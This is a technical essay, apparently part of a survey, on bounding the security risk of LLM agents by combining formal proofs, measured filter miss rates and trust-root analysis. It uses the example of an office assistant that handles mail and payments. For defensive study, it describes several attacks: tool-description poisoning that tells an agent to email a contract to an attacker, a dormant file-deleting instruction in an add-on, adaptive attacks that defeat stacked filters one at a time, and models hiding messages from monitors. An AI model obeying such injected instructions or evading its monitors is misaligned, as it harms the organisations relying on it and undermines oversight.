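The rule for scoring attacks should match the guarantee being tested. *Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers* (2026) uses a model to refine injections that try to move private information from one website to another, and counts an attack as failed if the agent leaks information other than what the attacker wanted. That rule suits a test of whether an attacker reached a particular goal, but in a test of a confidentiality proof, any protected information that crossed between the sites would be a counterexample.

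For defences that plan first, Nasr and colleagues recommend testing on tasks in which untrusted data can affect the agent's course of action. A test that used only tasks with fixed plans would just confirm what the design already guarantees.

A successful attack on a proved system reveals a false assumption or an unchecked path that engineers can fix, whereas a successful attack on a detector may lead only to more training. Even if no attack succeeds, the assumptions may be false in ways the testers didn't think of, or become false later. An attacker can wait for the company to connect a new tool or change a label, so the company should repeat the relevant tests before each such change takes effect.

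## Can proofs and measured rates be combined into one bound?

Yes, although the bound is weaker than it looks. The chance of harm is at most the chance that some assumption behind the proofs fails, plus the chance of a harm that the proofs don't cover. This holds even if an attacker makes several defences fail together. But it requires a proof about the whole system, which proofs about the parts don't always provide. For example, two components that each keep a secret can reveal it once a developer connects them. The chance that an assumption fails is also usually a matter of judgement, because no test measures it.

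### Rules about a single run

Some proofs combine easily. A run, or trace, is the sequence of actions that a system takes. In *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000), Fred Schneider studied mechanisms, such as reference monitors and firewalls, that stop a run when its next action would break a rule. He showed that such a mechanism can enforce a rule only if each run's compliance depends on that run alone and every violation happens at a definite point in the run. The ban on paying accounts outside the supplier list meets both conditions.

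If one check allows the set of runs *P*₁ and another allows the set *P*₂, a system with both checks allows only the runs in *P*₁ ∩ *P*₂. The company can therefore prove the supplier-list rule and the spending cap separately, and the assistant will satisfy both. A third check that only blocks actions can't invalidate either proof, because it can only remove runs. It may remove useful runs, and the proofs would still hold, because even an assistant that does nothing satisfies every rule of this kind.

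A monitor can't enforce a rule that something must eventually happen, such as the assistant recording every payment in the ledger, because the assistant might still add an entry later, however long it has been missing.

Secrecy is harder still because it depends on how different runs compare. Whether an email reveals a secret depends on what the assistant would have sent if the secret had been different, which a record of one run doesn't show. Monitors instead enforce a stricter rule that can be checked on a single run. Fred Schneider's example is a ban on sending any message after reading a file. This stops messages from leaking the file, but it also blocks harmless ones.

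### Two secure agents that leak when connected

In the late 1980s, Daryl McCullough showed that two components can each satisfy a secrecy property that the combined system violates. The property, generalized noninterference, is a version of noninterference for systems that can behave in several ways on the same input. It requires that outsiders cannot deduce from what they see whether a particular secret message arrived.

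A small example similar to McCullough's uses two agents. A mail agent receives confidential offers from bidders and exchanges private messages with a payments agent. Either agent may send a blank private message at any time. The mail agent chooses when to announce the end of the day. Each agent then publishes whether the number of private messages it has sent and received, including any offers, is odd or even.

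On its own, the mail agent reveals nothing about the offers. If another offer had arrived, the agent could have sent another blank message before ending the day, and the published result would have been the same. The payments agent can hide how many messages it receives in the same way.

Once the agents start messaging each other, each message adds one to both counts, so blank messages no longer hide whether an offer arrived. An offer adds one only to the mail agent's count. Suppose the agents exchange four messages. If no offer arrived, both publish "even". If one arrived, the mail agent publishes "odd" and the payments agent "even". An outsider who expects at most one offer can therefore tell whether it came.

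*On the Composition of Secure Systems* (Mantel, 2002) classifies the conditions under which such properties still hold when systems are combined. Generalized noninterference still holds if the connection is restricted so that the first component can send to the second but receives nothing back. In the example, the payments agent would then send its blank messages to another recipient, and those messages would hide the number it had received.

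The other repair is to strengthen the property to forward correctability, which also requires a component to be able to hide a secret message when a public one arrives immediately afterwards. The payments agent fails this requirement because, if the end-of-day announcement comes straight after a private message, the agent has no time to send a blank one. If components satisfy forward correctability, any system built by connecting them does too. Mantel found a slightly weaker property that is also preserved however the components are connected.

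He also points out that a component whose actions no outsider can observe satisfies most of these properties without any verification. A quarantined model comes close to this if its answers keep their secret label. But most agents that work together send messages in both directions, so proving secrecy for each one separately is not enough. Garby and colleagues' theorem avoids this problem for agents written as a single LLMbda program, because it covers the whole program, but it doesn't extend to agents that communicate through other software.

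### When a component drops the label

Combined systems also fail when a component loses information that a later check needs. In Peters-Gill and colleagues' three-agent system, planted text lost its untrusted status when one agent put it into an instruction to another. In *CONTINUITY*, Zheng and Yang (2026), the founders of ZAST.AI, call this kind of failure security-context discontinuity. Their remedy is a signed record that accompanies each action from the user's request to its execution.

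The paper's main example is a payment. A policy check approves a transfer of 5,000 from account 17 to "merchant 9", based on a verified invoice. "Merchant 9" is an alias, which a component called the adapter must replace with a bank account number. A faulty or hijacked adapter inserts the attacker's account. The adapter's signature is genuine, the action is a permitted type of payment, and a permit issued then would match the attacker's account exactly. Every local check passes, but nothing verifies that the account in the payment belongs to the merchant the policy check approved.

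In Continuity, a trusted directory must sign a statement that an alias belongs to a particular account. The statement applies to only one task and expires after a set time. A separate verifier compares it with the values before and after the change, so the adapter can't choose an account by itself.

Each component has a contract that specifies:

- what it requires of its input
- what it guarantees about its output
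- which fields it must leave unchanged
- which fields it may change, and what evidence it needs for each change.

Components fit together if each one's requirements follow from the guarantees of those before it. Zheng and Yang prove that the whole chain is secure under seven conditions:

1. A trusted authority has approved the task, and trusted issuers have signed the record of where its data came from.
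2. The components' contracts fit together.
3. Every change to a protected field has independently checked evidence.
4. No component can add authority or remove an untrusted label without separate signed permission.
5. The final permit covers the exact action that runs.
6. Immediately before the action, the last check confirms that the permit is still valid and unused.
7. Every route to the action goes through that last check.

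If these conditions hold and the attacker can't forge signatures, every protected action has a complete chain of valid approvals, even if the attacker controls the model. The proof follows the chain one component at a time, as David and colleagues' proof did with effects. A related theorem shows that if a component removes a label that a later decision depends on, a request that should pass can look identical to one that shouldn't. The later component must then block both or risk allowing the wrong one.

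The system lets untrusted data influence an action only through a signed exception for one value in one field. In the payment tests, an exception could cover an invoice amount of up to 20,000 cents. If the trusted software that reads invoices extracts the wrong amount, the chain of signatures preserves the mistake.

Zheng and Yang tested the design against 2,560 attacks, which they made by placing 32 types of fault in four kinds of work and varying the details of each combination 20 times. They used no language model and assumed that the attacker already controlled the planning. The full system stopped every attack. A system with a policy check and a permit for the exact final action, but no verified link between them, allowed 65.6% of attacks. The full system also completed all 700 ordinary tasks and referred all 200 ambiguous ones for further approval.

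The 65.6% shows that the missing link matters, but it doesn't measure how often real systems fail, because Zheng and Yang chose the faults and built the weaker systems themselves as controls for their own design. Removing one safeguard at a time was more informative. Without the records of where each field came from, 24 of the 128 combinations of fault and work succeeded again. Removing the separate check on growing authority let none through, because other checks blocked the same faults.

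### Tools that are safe only separately

A chain can keep every label and satisfy every tool's own rule and still do harm. If one tool may read internal documents and another may send data to websites, together they can publish a confidential contract without either breaking its rule. This doesn't contradict Fred Schneider's result, because both rules still hold, but neither forbids the leak. Preventing it requires a rule about the whole run, such as his ban on sending after reading.

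The Microsoft study *Securing Multi-Tool AI Agent Chains With Dynamic, Real-Time Compositional Policies* (Schneider, Faujdar and colleagues, 2026) derives such rules automatically. It cites research on 20 agent applications in which 302 of 365 confirmed vulnerabilities required more than one tool. In another study it cites, attacks made of a sequence of prompts that each scored under 2% for harmfulness succeeded more than 90% of the time. A filter that judges one step at a time would be unlikely to detect such attacks.

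In their system, every tool has a policy that states how sensitive its data may be, whether it sends data outside, and where and for how long it may run. Before a session starts, software combines the policies of all the tools the agent has requested and keeps the strictest value for each item: the highest sensitivity, the shortest time limit, and only the network zones that every tool allows. Adding a tool can therefore never loosen the combined policy. During the session, the software also tracks the sensitivity of the data the agent has read. If the agent reads confidential salary data and then tries to upload a file to an outside service, the software blocks the upload and ends the session.

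Schneider and colleagues tried every pair and triple of tools from a catalogue of 32, governed by 16 policies. In the strict mode, every tool must have clearance for the most sensitive data that any tool in the chain handles. The looser mode drops that requirement but still keeps non-public data away from tools that send data outside.

| Combination | Number tried | Blocked in strict mode | Blocked in looser mode |
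|---|---|---|---|
| Pairs of policies | 120 | 79.2% | 42.5% |
| Triples of policies | 560 | 95.5% | 60.5% |
| Pairs of tools, in both orders | 992 | 71.0% | 32.5% |
| Triples of tools | 4,960 | 90.7% | 47.4% |

These percentages describe the catalogue and its policies. They don't mean that 79.2% of real tool pairs are dangerous, and the figures could be very different for another company's catalogue.

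Checking policies in pairs can miss a conflict among three. Suppose the mail tool may run in the office network or the cloud, the payment tool in the cloud or the bank's network, and the archive tool in the office or the bank's network. Each pair of tools shares a zone, but no zone is allowed for all three. In the catalogue, however, every triple of policies whose three pairs passed also passed. Triples were blocked more often than pairs only because a triple contains three pairs, any of which can fail.

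The method is also much too coarse for the office assistant. The email policy conflicted with every other policy in the catalogue, in both modes, so an agent that needed to read internal files and send email could not have started work. FIDES avoids this problem with its lists of permitted readers. Schneider and colleagues defend their caution by arguing that a company can recover from an overly strict policy but not from a leak.

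### Rules about the whole plan

A monitor can't enforce the rule that every payment must reach the ledger. CaMeLoT's search of the plan can check this rule instead, by finding any path that makes a payment but ends without a ledger entry.

Nikolaou and colleagues tested this with an agent that responds to security alerts. They wrote seven rules, including that the agent must get approval before cutting a computer off from the network, and that it must resolve or escalate every incident it opens. They also wrote one unsafe plan for each rule. CaMeLoT caught all seven plans, while a simplified version of CaMeL that tracked only untrusted data caught one. The team deliberately chose rules outside CaMeL's scope, so the scores show only what kind of rule each system can check.

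In a second test, a model wrote the plans itself in response to requests, one of which was to skip the approval because time was short. CaMeLoT rejected all four unsafe plans, and the simplified CaMeL rejected none.

Checks made before a run and checks made during it complement each other. CaMeLoT could reproduce 22 of the 28 policies that CaMeL applies to AgentDojo's tools before the run, but the other six can only be checked during it. A plan that includes a ledger entry also doesn't guarantee that the entry succeeds. If the ledger software crashes after the payment, the rule requiring the entry is broken even though the proof about the plan was correct.

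### Three filters that each miss 5%

Measured rates are harder to combine than proofs. Suppose the company puts three filters in front of the assistant to detect hostile mail, and each misses 5% of attacks in tests. If their mistakes are independent, the share of attacks that gets past all three is

0.05 × 0.05 × 0.05 = 0.000125,

or 0.0125%, which is one attack in 8,000. If all three miss the same attacks, the share is 5%, and the second and third filters add nothing. The three separate rates can't show which figure is closer to the truth.

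Even a small overlap in what the filters miss can greatly increase the combined miss rate. Suppose 1% of the test attacks fool every filter, and the filters' mistakes on the rest are independent. If each filter misses 5% of attacks overall, about 1.01% get past all three. That is roughly 80 times the rate for fully independent filters, and adding more filters with the same blind spot cannot bring it below 1%.

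The combined false-alarm rate is more predictable. If each of the three filters blocks 5% of honest mail, together they block between 5% and 15%, depending on how much their false alarms overlap.

The filters could fail together for several reasons. They may use similar models trained on similar attacks, and they all process the same emails. Brauchler warns that a model that monitors another is also vulnerable to injection, so one email could contain an instruction for the assistant and another for its reviewer. Different models also seem to share some weaknesses, since Zhang and colleagues' pop-ups and Foerster and colleagues' altered image each fooled more than one model.

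These experiments don't measure the joint failure rate of the company's three filters, and multiplying the separate rates is no substitute for measuring it. To measure it, testers have to attack all three filters at once and count the attacks that reach the assistant.

### Why an attacker makes the filters fail together

If 1% of attacks fool every filter, an attacker wants to find one of those and keep using it, rather than pick emails at random from the company's test set. Once he finds one, his success rate against the filters is close to 100%, although the average over the test set is still 1.01%.

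An attacker can get past three independent filters much faster if he learns which filter stopped each attempt. Without that information, he would need an average of 8,000 random attempts. With it, he can find wording that passes the first filter, keep that wording while he works on the second, and then do the same for the third. If the changes he makes to pass one filter don't make the wording fail a filter it already passed, he needs an average of 20 attempts for each, or 60 in total.

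The 5% figure is the highest possible joint miss rate only for attacks like those in the tests, and an adaptive attacker writes different ones. Adaptive attacks raised miss rates from near zero to more than 90% for some of the defences that Nasr and colleagues tested. Three filters that each miss 90% of attacks would together let through 73% even if their mistakes were independent, and up to 90% if they weren't.

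A filter and a supplier-list check are less likely to fail together, because wording that fools the filter has no effect on the list. But an intruder who takes over the server they both run on could switch them both off. Testing each layer separately doesn't show that they fail independently, which requires an argument about shared causes of failure like this one.

### Adding failures

When several filters guard against the same harm, an attacker has to get past all of them. But the parts of a larger system usually have different jobs, so the system can fail if any one of them does. Villa and colleagues analyse a simple case in which one model proposes answers and a second accepts or rejects them. Each model is responsible for a different requirement; for example, the first might have to give useful answers and the second might have to reject harmful ones.

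If the first model meets its requirement with probability *p*₁ and the second with probability *p*₂, the probability *p* that the whole system meets both satisfies

1 − *p* ≤ (1 − *p*₁) + (1 − *p*₂).

If a system can fail only when at least one of its two parts fails, and each part fails 5% of the time, then the system fails at most 10% of the time. This holds even if the failures aren't independent, because the chance that at least one of two events happens can never exceed the sum of their chances. The same reasoning works against an attacker. The proof turns any attack on the whole system into an attack on each part, and shows that the whole can fail only if at least one part does.

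### The joint bound

The same argument combines proofs with measured rates. Let *H* be the event that the assistant causes harm during a given month, and let *A* be the event that every assumption behind the proofs holds throughout that month. Harm happens either when an assumption has failed or when they all hold, so

P(*H*) = P(*H* and not *A*) + P(*H* and *A*).

The first term can't be larger than the chance that an assumption fails, which gives

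P(*H*) ≤ P(not *A*) + P(*H* and *A*).

If all the assumptions hold, the proofs rule out every harm they cover. The only harm left is uncovered harm, *U*, such as a false summary. The bound becomes

P(*H*) ≤ P(not *A*) + P(*U* and *A*).

If there are several assumptions, P(not *A*) is at most the sum of their separate chances of failing.

This bound is conservative because it counts every failed assumption as a harm, even though a gap in the checks might exist for a month without any attacker finding it.

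Both terms must refer to the same system over the same period. An attack success rate is a chance per attack, so the company has to estimate how many attacks will arrive in a month. It also has to test the assistant with its checks switched on and score the harms that the proofs don't cover. A rate measured on the model without those checks would mostly reflect attacks that they would have stopped.

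### The bound for the office assistant

The office assistant's risks have four kinds of support.

| Risk | What limits it | Kind of support |
|---|---|---|
| Payment to an unlisted account, with assumptions intact | Supplier-list check | Proved impossible |
| Secret text mailed to someone who may not read it, with assumptions intact | Labels and the permitted-reader rule | Proved impossible |
| Overpayment to a listed supplier | Spending budget | Capped in dollars |
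| Leak through the choice of permitted actions | Limits on the number of runs and possible results | Capped in bits |
| False inbox summary | Resistance of the model | Measured |
| Wrong label, unchecked route to the bank, altered supplier list or faulty payment counter | Design reviews and targeted tests | Argued |

Suppose the company wants to bound the chance of a payment to an unlisted account, a directly mailed secret or a false summary next month. Its testers have made 299 independent attacks on the summary and none has succeeded, so the 95% upper limit on the success rate is 1% per attack. It expects no more than five hostile mails, which makes the chance of a false summary at most 5%. After reviewing the design, its engineers put the chance that any assumption fails at 1%. The joint bound is

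1% + 5% = 6%.

The capped risks don't appear in this sum, because a cap limits the size of a loss and not its probability. They belong in a bound on money. Let *C* be the most that the assistant can lose through payments while every assumption holds, and *M* the most it can lose otherwise. The expected loss *L* then satisfies

E(*L*) ≤ *C* + *M* × P(not *A*).

With the $10,000 budget described earlier and $400,000 in the company's account, this comes to

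$10,000 + $400,000 × 1% = $14,000.

If the engineers had put the chance of a failed assumption at 5%, the bound would be $30,000. The bound therefore depends heavily on a number nobody has measured. If the bank enforces the budget, a fault in the company's own software no longer exposes the whole account, and the loss stays within $10,000 as long as the bank's limit works. Reducing *M* this way is usually easier than proving that P(not *A*) is small.

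### Where the probabilities come from

The 1% for a failed assumption reflects how confident the engineers are that they would have found any unchecked route to the bank. It isn't a frequency, because such a route either exists or it doesn't. Other engineers could reasonably choose a different figure.

Zheng and Yang's test doesn't supply this number. Their system stopped all 2,560 attacks, and the usual rule of three would put an upper limit of about 0.12% on its failure rate, but they warn against reading the result as a failure probability. The attacks were variations on 32 faults the researchers had thought of, not a random sample of the faults in real systems. A fault outside the list could defeat the system every time.

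Such tests are still worth running because each one can reveal a false assumption. The engineers can also become more confident as they rule out specific routes and faults, although the number they end up with is a judgement informed by the tests.

The measured 5% also depends on the assumption that next month's attacks will resemble the 299 in the test. That may be reasonable for mass-produced injection emails, but not for attacks by someone who studies the assistant or by a supplier who behaves honestly until the testing is over. Against such people, the chance of a false summary could be close to 100%, so a total of 6% would be badly misleading.

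The company should calculate a separate bound for each harm before adding them up. The bound for payments to unlisted accounts doesn't use a measured attack rate, so it stays at 1% however cleverly the attacker writes, provided that the engineers allowed for a determined attacker when they judged the assumptions. The bound for false summaries does use a measured rate, and it may be too low if real attacks are stronger than those in the test. A single total would hide this difference, which may matter more to the company than the total itself.

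### Layered probabilities and security boundaries

Some people would say that agent security is a matter of probability. No check is perfect and every proof has assumptions that might be false, so they would add layers of protection until the remaining risk is small enough. Cryptography seems to support this view, since its definitions allow an attacker a negligible advantage, which is itself a probability.

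Brauchler takes the opposite view of filters and says that "every guardrail can and will be bypassed". He compares AI developers to web developers in an imagined history who respond to the first threats by inventing a firewall that filters traffic. The web developers keep relying on the firewall as websites become more powerful, and the websites remain vulnerable.

The joint bound partly supports the first view, because its final answer is a probability that never reaches zero. But it matters whether an attacker can raise that probability. Each new guess at a random 128-bit key has about one chance in 3.4 × 10³⁸ of being right, however the attacker chooses it. A filter's 5% miss rate is an average over other people's attacks, and he can raise it by writing better ones. Treating the two numbers as the same kind of quantity makes three weak filters look like a strong defence.

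There is also a theoretical reason to doubt that a small filter would be enough. Villa and colleagues discuss an earlier proof in which a malicious model hides messages in harmless-looking text, using a code that no efficient filter can detect. The proof assumes that the recipient can decode something the filter can't. Villa and colleagues question how well this assumption fits a model that is supposed to work correctly, but they accept that a filter may have to be about as complex as the model it checks. Such a filter would be far too large to meet Anderson's size condition.

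Brauchler is therefore right that a filter shouldn't be the reason a company allows a dangerous action. It would be a mistake to drop the supplier-list check because three filters appear to miss only one attack in 8,000. Filters are still useful where no fixed rule applies. They can stop many ordinary attempts to falsify the inbox summary, and a blocked email can alert the company that someone is attacking it. The company can include that benefit in the measured term if it tests all the filters together against people trying to get past them.

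## What remains when the trusted root is compromised?

The joint bound includes the chance that an assumption fails, but some failures do far more damage than others. An attacker who takes over an ordinary component defeats only the checks that rely on it, while one who takes over a root, such as the key that signs every permission, defeats all the checks derived from it at once. Only guarantees that rest on a different root survive, and the office assistant may have just one, a payment limit enforced by the bank. Proofs and special hardware can make the trusted base smaller, but people still have to trust part of it without proof.

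### What the guarantees rest on

Trust assumptions differ between designs. Costa and colleagues assume that the model, the system messages, the tool descriptions and the user's messages to FIDES are trustworthy. They also treat all of these as public, so a password in a system message would have no protection. Trusting the user's messages is risky if the user pastes in a stranger's text. *PerMIT* (2026), which protects an agent's long-term memory, therefore relies on a channel that distinguishes typed text from pasted text.

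Zheng and Yang's list for Continuity is longer. It includes the authorities that approve tasks and vouch for data, the assignment of each component to a role, the current policy, the verifier and the final check before each action. It also includes the keys and the procedures for issuing, replacing and revoking them.

*AgentKernel* (Zou, Guo and colleagues, 2026) describes a security layer between agents and the operating system. A central registry signs every agent's identity, and a local program called the agent kernel holds the private keys. Agents may reach the model, their tools and stored data only through three adapters. The registry, the agent kernel and the adapters all belong to the trusted base, along with the part of the operating system that limits each tool's access to files and the network.

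*SoK* (2026) adds the password store and the service that issues credentials. *Agent libOS* (2026) includes the Python interpreter, the storage system and the person who approves an action.

The guarantee also assumes that the policy is right. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) points out that a policy can be enforced without capturing what the user wants. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) excludes from its guarantee unsafe actions that the policy permits, and any policy that the agent is allowed to change. It is easy to write such a policy by accident. If the supplier list is a spreadsheet and a rule lets the assistant edit spreadsheets, the assistant can add a supplier.

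### What fails with each part

Suppose the company runs the agent loop, the labels and the checks on one rented server, which also holds the passwords for its mail and its bank account. The bank enforces the $10,000 budget, and an accountant can renew it only from a separate device. This budget limits payments in every row of the table, so the last column lists only the other limits on the loss.

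| Part the attacker controls | Guarantee lost | Guarantee that survives | What else limits the loss |
|---|---|---|---|
| Policy author | Every rule the author may change, including the supplier list | Rules that somebody else controls | A second person's approval of each change |
| Labelling code | The trusted-action and permitted-reader rules | The supplier-list check, which doesn't use labels | A list of permitted recipients |
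| Policy engine | Every rule it enforces | Rules enforced on other machines | A separate firewall |
| Credential store | Complete mediation, because the attacker can use the mail and bank accounts directly | Rules for the agent's own calls | Narrow rights and early expiry for each credential |
| Tool description | The claim that an outsider's text can't trigger an action | The supplier-list check and the strict permitted-reader rule | Review of every new or changed description |
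| Build chain | Every rule enforced by the software it produces | Rules enforced by software from another source | Comparison with an independent build |
| Operating system | Every rule enforced on the server, and the secrecy of its data | Rules enforced on other machines | The amount of data the server can read |
| Hardware | The same, and any proof of which software is running | Rules enforced on other machines | The amount of data the server can read |
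| One component's signing key | The honesty of that component's output | Independent checks on that output | The changes its contract allows |
| Root signing key | Every permission that derives from the key | Rules that rest on another key | Revocation by someone who holds another key |

The bank's budget doesn't protect confidential data. Someone who controls the operating system can copy every document the server can read, and the company can't get those copies back. The best protection is to give the server access only to documents it needs. The inbox summary wasn't guaranteed to be true even before the compromise, because that depended on the model.

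### A poisoned tool description

The program sends the model a description of each tool with every query, and an outside company that supplies a tool usually writes its description too. *Model Context Protocol Threat Modeling and Analyzing Vulnerabilities to Prompt Injection* (2026) defines tool poisoning as a form of prompt injection in which the attacker puts instructions in these descriptions. The model may read the instructions even if it never uses the tool.

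Suppose the company adds a currency converter whose description contains an instruction to email the latest contract to the attacker. FIDES treats tool descriptions as trusted, so the history stays trusted and the call passes the trusted-action rule. The strict permitted-reader rule still blocks the email, because the attacker isn't among the contract's readers. But Microsoft's looser policies allow a message if the context is trusted, so the email would be sent. A payment to the attacker's account would still fail the supplier-list check.

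Somebody has to review the tool descriptions, because labelling them as untrusted would make the history untrusted before the assistant had read any mail, and the trusted-action rule would then block every consequential action. Continuity keeps a digital fingerprint of each approved tool specification, so a supplier can't change one unnoticed after the review, but the reviewer may still have missed something.

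The code behind a harmless description can also be hostile. In September 2025, the security firm Koi Security reported on a package that let agents send email through Postmark. After several harmless versions, its developer had added a line that secretly copied him on every message. The permitted-reader rule wouldn't have caught this, because it checks the recipients in the tool call and the package added another one afterwards.

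A tool that runs on the company's own server can do more damage. *Agent libOS* notes that such a tool may run with all the rights of the account that started it. It could then edit the supplier list or read the bank password without making a tool call.

### Stolen keys

Continuity limits what an attacker can do with one component's key. An attacker who steals the key of the adapter, which fills in account numbers, can't use it to sign the directory statement that a new number needs, approve a task, or impersonate a different component. Zheng and Yang acknowledge that the attacker can still exploit the adapter's contract wherever it is too permissive.

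An attacker with a key that can approve tasks doesn't need to misrepresent their authority to the later components. They issue an approval that covers the payment they want, and each component correctly verifies that the action stays within it. The rule that no component may add authority doesn't help, because the initial approval already grants enough.

When Zheng and Yang removed the check on who had started and approved a task, attacks succeeded again in 16 of the 128 combinations of fault and type of work. When they removed the rule that ties each key to its role, attacks succeeded again in four. These numbers depend on the faults they chose, and an attacker with a root key needs only one successful attack. Their prototype doesn't include key replacement, approval by several parties or hardware protection for keys.

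In *AID-Guard* (2026), the damage depends on which key or component is compromised. A stolen confirmation key lets an attacker fake the user's presence but not forge the original authorisation. A stolen key for signing capabilities is useless by itself, because the server keeps its own record of each capability and a forged one has no matching entry. An attacker who takes over that record store, the gateway, the current root signer or the component that performs the actions defeats the corresponding core guarantee. A company can get some of this protection cheaply by keeping the records on a different machine from the signing key.

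### AgentKernel's residual risks

AgentKernel gives each agent a signed certificate that sets its maximum permissions. An agent can create another agent only with permissions that its own certificate includes, so a careless policy can't exceed the limit the registry signed. Zou and colleagues acknowledge that this leaves some things unprotected.

- The registry's signing key is a single point of trust. Anyone who steals it can forge the identity of any agent.
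- The three adapters have to be the only way out. An agent that keeps a password of its own can go around them, and preventing this is up to whoever installs the system.
- The software may assign labels that are too permissive when an attacker deliberately blurs the boundary between trusted and untrusted text.
- One of the input filters uses a language model, which an attacker can learn to fool.
- The limits on files and network access use a Linux feature called eBPF, which has limited availability on other operating systems.
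- Nobody has yet checked the design's security properties by machine.

They also exclude physical attacks, leaks through timing or power use, and an attacker who controls the host's operating system.

Zou and colleagues argue that an attacker has to defeat several independent mechanisms, because identity, input, memory and actions each have their own checks. They also concede that these checks share information. A false identity can make the input filter too permissive, which can lead to wrong labels in memory and limits on tools that are too loose. They propose that each part verify what it receives from the others.

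This should catch many false claims by a single part. It doesn't catch a forged certificate, because the other parts would find the registry's signature valid. The forged certificate would also set the maximum permissions for the agent's tools. Each tool's own declaration of what it needs would still restrict access, unless the attacker could change that too.

### More checks under one root

A compromised root has the same effect as a blind spot that several filters share. If the root has a 1% chance of failing, adding checks that depend on it cannot bring the chance of a successful attack below 1%. Extra checks may raise that chance if each one needs a copy of the signing key or runs with administrator rights, because the attacker has more targets.

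In *Protecting Context and Prompts*, Rajagopalan and Rao (2026) describe five layers of defence that they say fail independently: a filter for forbidden patterns, checks at every tool, signed prompts, a tamper-evident history, and an optional comparison with the user's original request. They report detecting every attack in six categories, but their threat model assumes that nobody has compromised the agent registry.

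Each tool check gets the caller's public key and the tool's policy from the registry. An attacker who controls the registry can replace the assistant's key with their own and then sign any request. They can also replace the tools' keys, which protect the history, and loosen the tools' policies, so at least three of the layers fail together. The organisation's policy comes from a separate store, so anything it forbids stays forbidden unless the attacker controls that store as well.

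*Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (Matsuoka, 2026) extends the problem to many agents and to recovery. Matsuoka imagines a popular add-on with a dormant instruction to delete files, which an ordinary-looking email triggers months later. Every company that installed the add-on is exposed, so their failures are not independent. If the agents' passwords also give access to the backups, the attack can destroy those too. Even if the backups survive, restoring them may bring back the dormant instruction along with the files. As of early August 2026, Matsuoka had found no public record of a complete attack of this kind, although researchers have demonstrated the individual steps.

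### Splitting tasks and splitting trust

Dividing a system into parts doesn't necessarily divide the trust placed in it. *SecureClaw* (Ma and Schmid, 2026) separates access to secrets from permission to act. A gateway stores each secret and gives the agent a reference number and a short summary. A second component, the executor, retrieves the secret and performs the action only after checking that the action's details exactly match an approved request.

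The division works well against a hijacked agent. With GPT-4o mini, AgentDojo attacks succeeded 0.64% of the time, versus 31.48% without protection. The two halves also address different threats. Faramesh, a rival defence, stopped every attack on a benchmark of harmful actions, but on a benchmark of leaks, secrets leaked in 93.95% of cases, no fewer than with an unprotected agent.

Ma and Schmid state that the design fails if an attacker compromises either the gateway or the executor. Whoever controls the executor can perform actions and read the secrets it retrieves. If the trust were split, an attacker would have to take over several parties to cause a single harm.

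### Labels with separate owners

*A Decentralized Model for Information Flow Control* (Andrew Myers and Barbara Liskov, 1997) describes a model in which several parties can each restrict the same data. Each owner lists the permitted readers, and only people on every list may read the data. An owner can relax their own list but nobody else's.

Suppose the office assistant holds a price agreement with Acme. The company's list is {lawyer, auditor}, and Acme's is {lawyer, accountant}, so only the lawyer may read it. An attacker who takes over the company's authority can add himself to the company's list. The result is

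{lawyer, auditor, attacker} ∩ {lawyer, accountant} = {lawyer},

and he still can't read the agreement.

This protects only data that another party has also restricted. It also assumes that he hasn't taken over the software that compares the lists. If that software runs on the company's server, someone who controls the server can ignore Acme's list. To prevent that, Acme would have to hold part of the decryption key or keep the agreement on its own server.

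### Approval by several parties

A company can require *k* of *n* parties to approve an action, such as adding a supplier. If an attacker controls each party independently with probability *q*, the chance that he controls enough of them is

Σ C(*n*, *i*) *qⁱ* (1 − *q*)^(*n*−*i*), summed from *i* = *k* to *n*,

where C(*n*, *i*) is the number of ways to choose *i* parties from *n*. With *q* = 1%, requiring two of three approvals gives a chance of about 0.03%, compared with 1% for a single approver. Requiring all three lowers it to 0.0001%, but then an attacker can block every change by controlling just one of them, which has a chance of about 3%.

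These figures depend heavily on the approvers being compromised independently. If all three approvers log in through the same service, and an attacker has a 0.5% chance of taking it over, the two-of-three figure rises from 0.03% to about 0.53%.

In February 2025, thieves stole about $1.5 billion in cryptocurrency from the exchange Bybit, although the transfer needed several people's approval. The approvers all used software from a company called Safe, which said the attackers had taken over a developer's machine. The attackers changed the software so that it displayed an ordinary transfer while the approvers signed a different one. Having separate keys didn't protect the approvers, because they all relied on the same software to show them what they were signing. For the office assistant, at least one approver should therefore check new account numbers with software from a different supplier.

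### Outside limits and revocation

The bank enforces the payment limit with its own computers, staff and keys, so the limit holds even if the company's server is completely compromised. But if the password for raising the limit is stored on that server, whoever controls the server can raise it. The company should keep the password on another device, and a delay before any increase takes effect would give the accountant time to object.

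Revocation shortens the time an attacker can use what he has stolen. Suppose a stolen credential expires after *T* hours, the company revokes it after *d* hours, and the news takes another *u* hours to reach every check. He can use it for at most

min(*T*, *d* + *u*) hours.

A thief who steals a one-hour payment permission can use it for at most an hour, even if nobody notices the theft for three days. But if he steals the signing key, he can issue himself a new permission every hour until the company replaces the key.

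Immediately before each action, Continuity checks for revocation, which keeps *u* small. In AgentKernel, revoking an agent's certificate also invalidates the certificates of all the agents it created. Neither measure is enough if the stolen root key also signs the revocation notices, because the attacker could then sign false ones. A second key, kept offline, should be able to replace the root key.

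### Attestation

The company might rent its server from a cloud provider whose staff could alter the software. Attestation can detect such changes. The processor contains a secret that the server's owner isn't supposed to be able to read, and it uses a key derived from that secret to sign a report of which software it started. The bank could accept payment requests only from a server whose report shows that it is running the approved supplier-list check. The report wouldn't reveal an undiscovered fault in that check.

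AMD's server processors derive the key from both the chip's root secret and the version of its firmware, the built-in software that produces the report. In simplified form, the root secret is *s*₂₅₅, and each earlier value comes from a one-way function *H*:

*s*ᵥ₋₁ = *H*(*s*ᵥ).

Firmware version *v* receives only *s*ᵥ, from which it can calculate the values for older versions but not for newer ones. An attacker who breaks into old, faulty firmware therefore shouldn't be able to pass it off as the current version.

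Shen and Qin (2026), in *Insecure Despite Proven Updated*, extracted the root secret from a processor in AMD's EPYC Milan series, the first to support this system. The attack uses only software but requires control of the server and its firmware. Attestation is meant to protect customers from someone with that control. They first used a flaw that AMD had disclosed in 2021, without technical details, to run their own code. They then found that the chip prevented software from reading the secret but didn't adequately prevent changes to it, which let them work out its value.

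An attacker who has the root secret can calculate the key for any firmware version and sign a false report. The bank might then accept payments from a server with no supplier-list check. Updating the firmware doesn't solve this, because the attacker can calculate the new key too. The bank could refuse reports from the affected generation of chips, or treat them as weak evidence.

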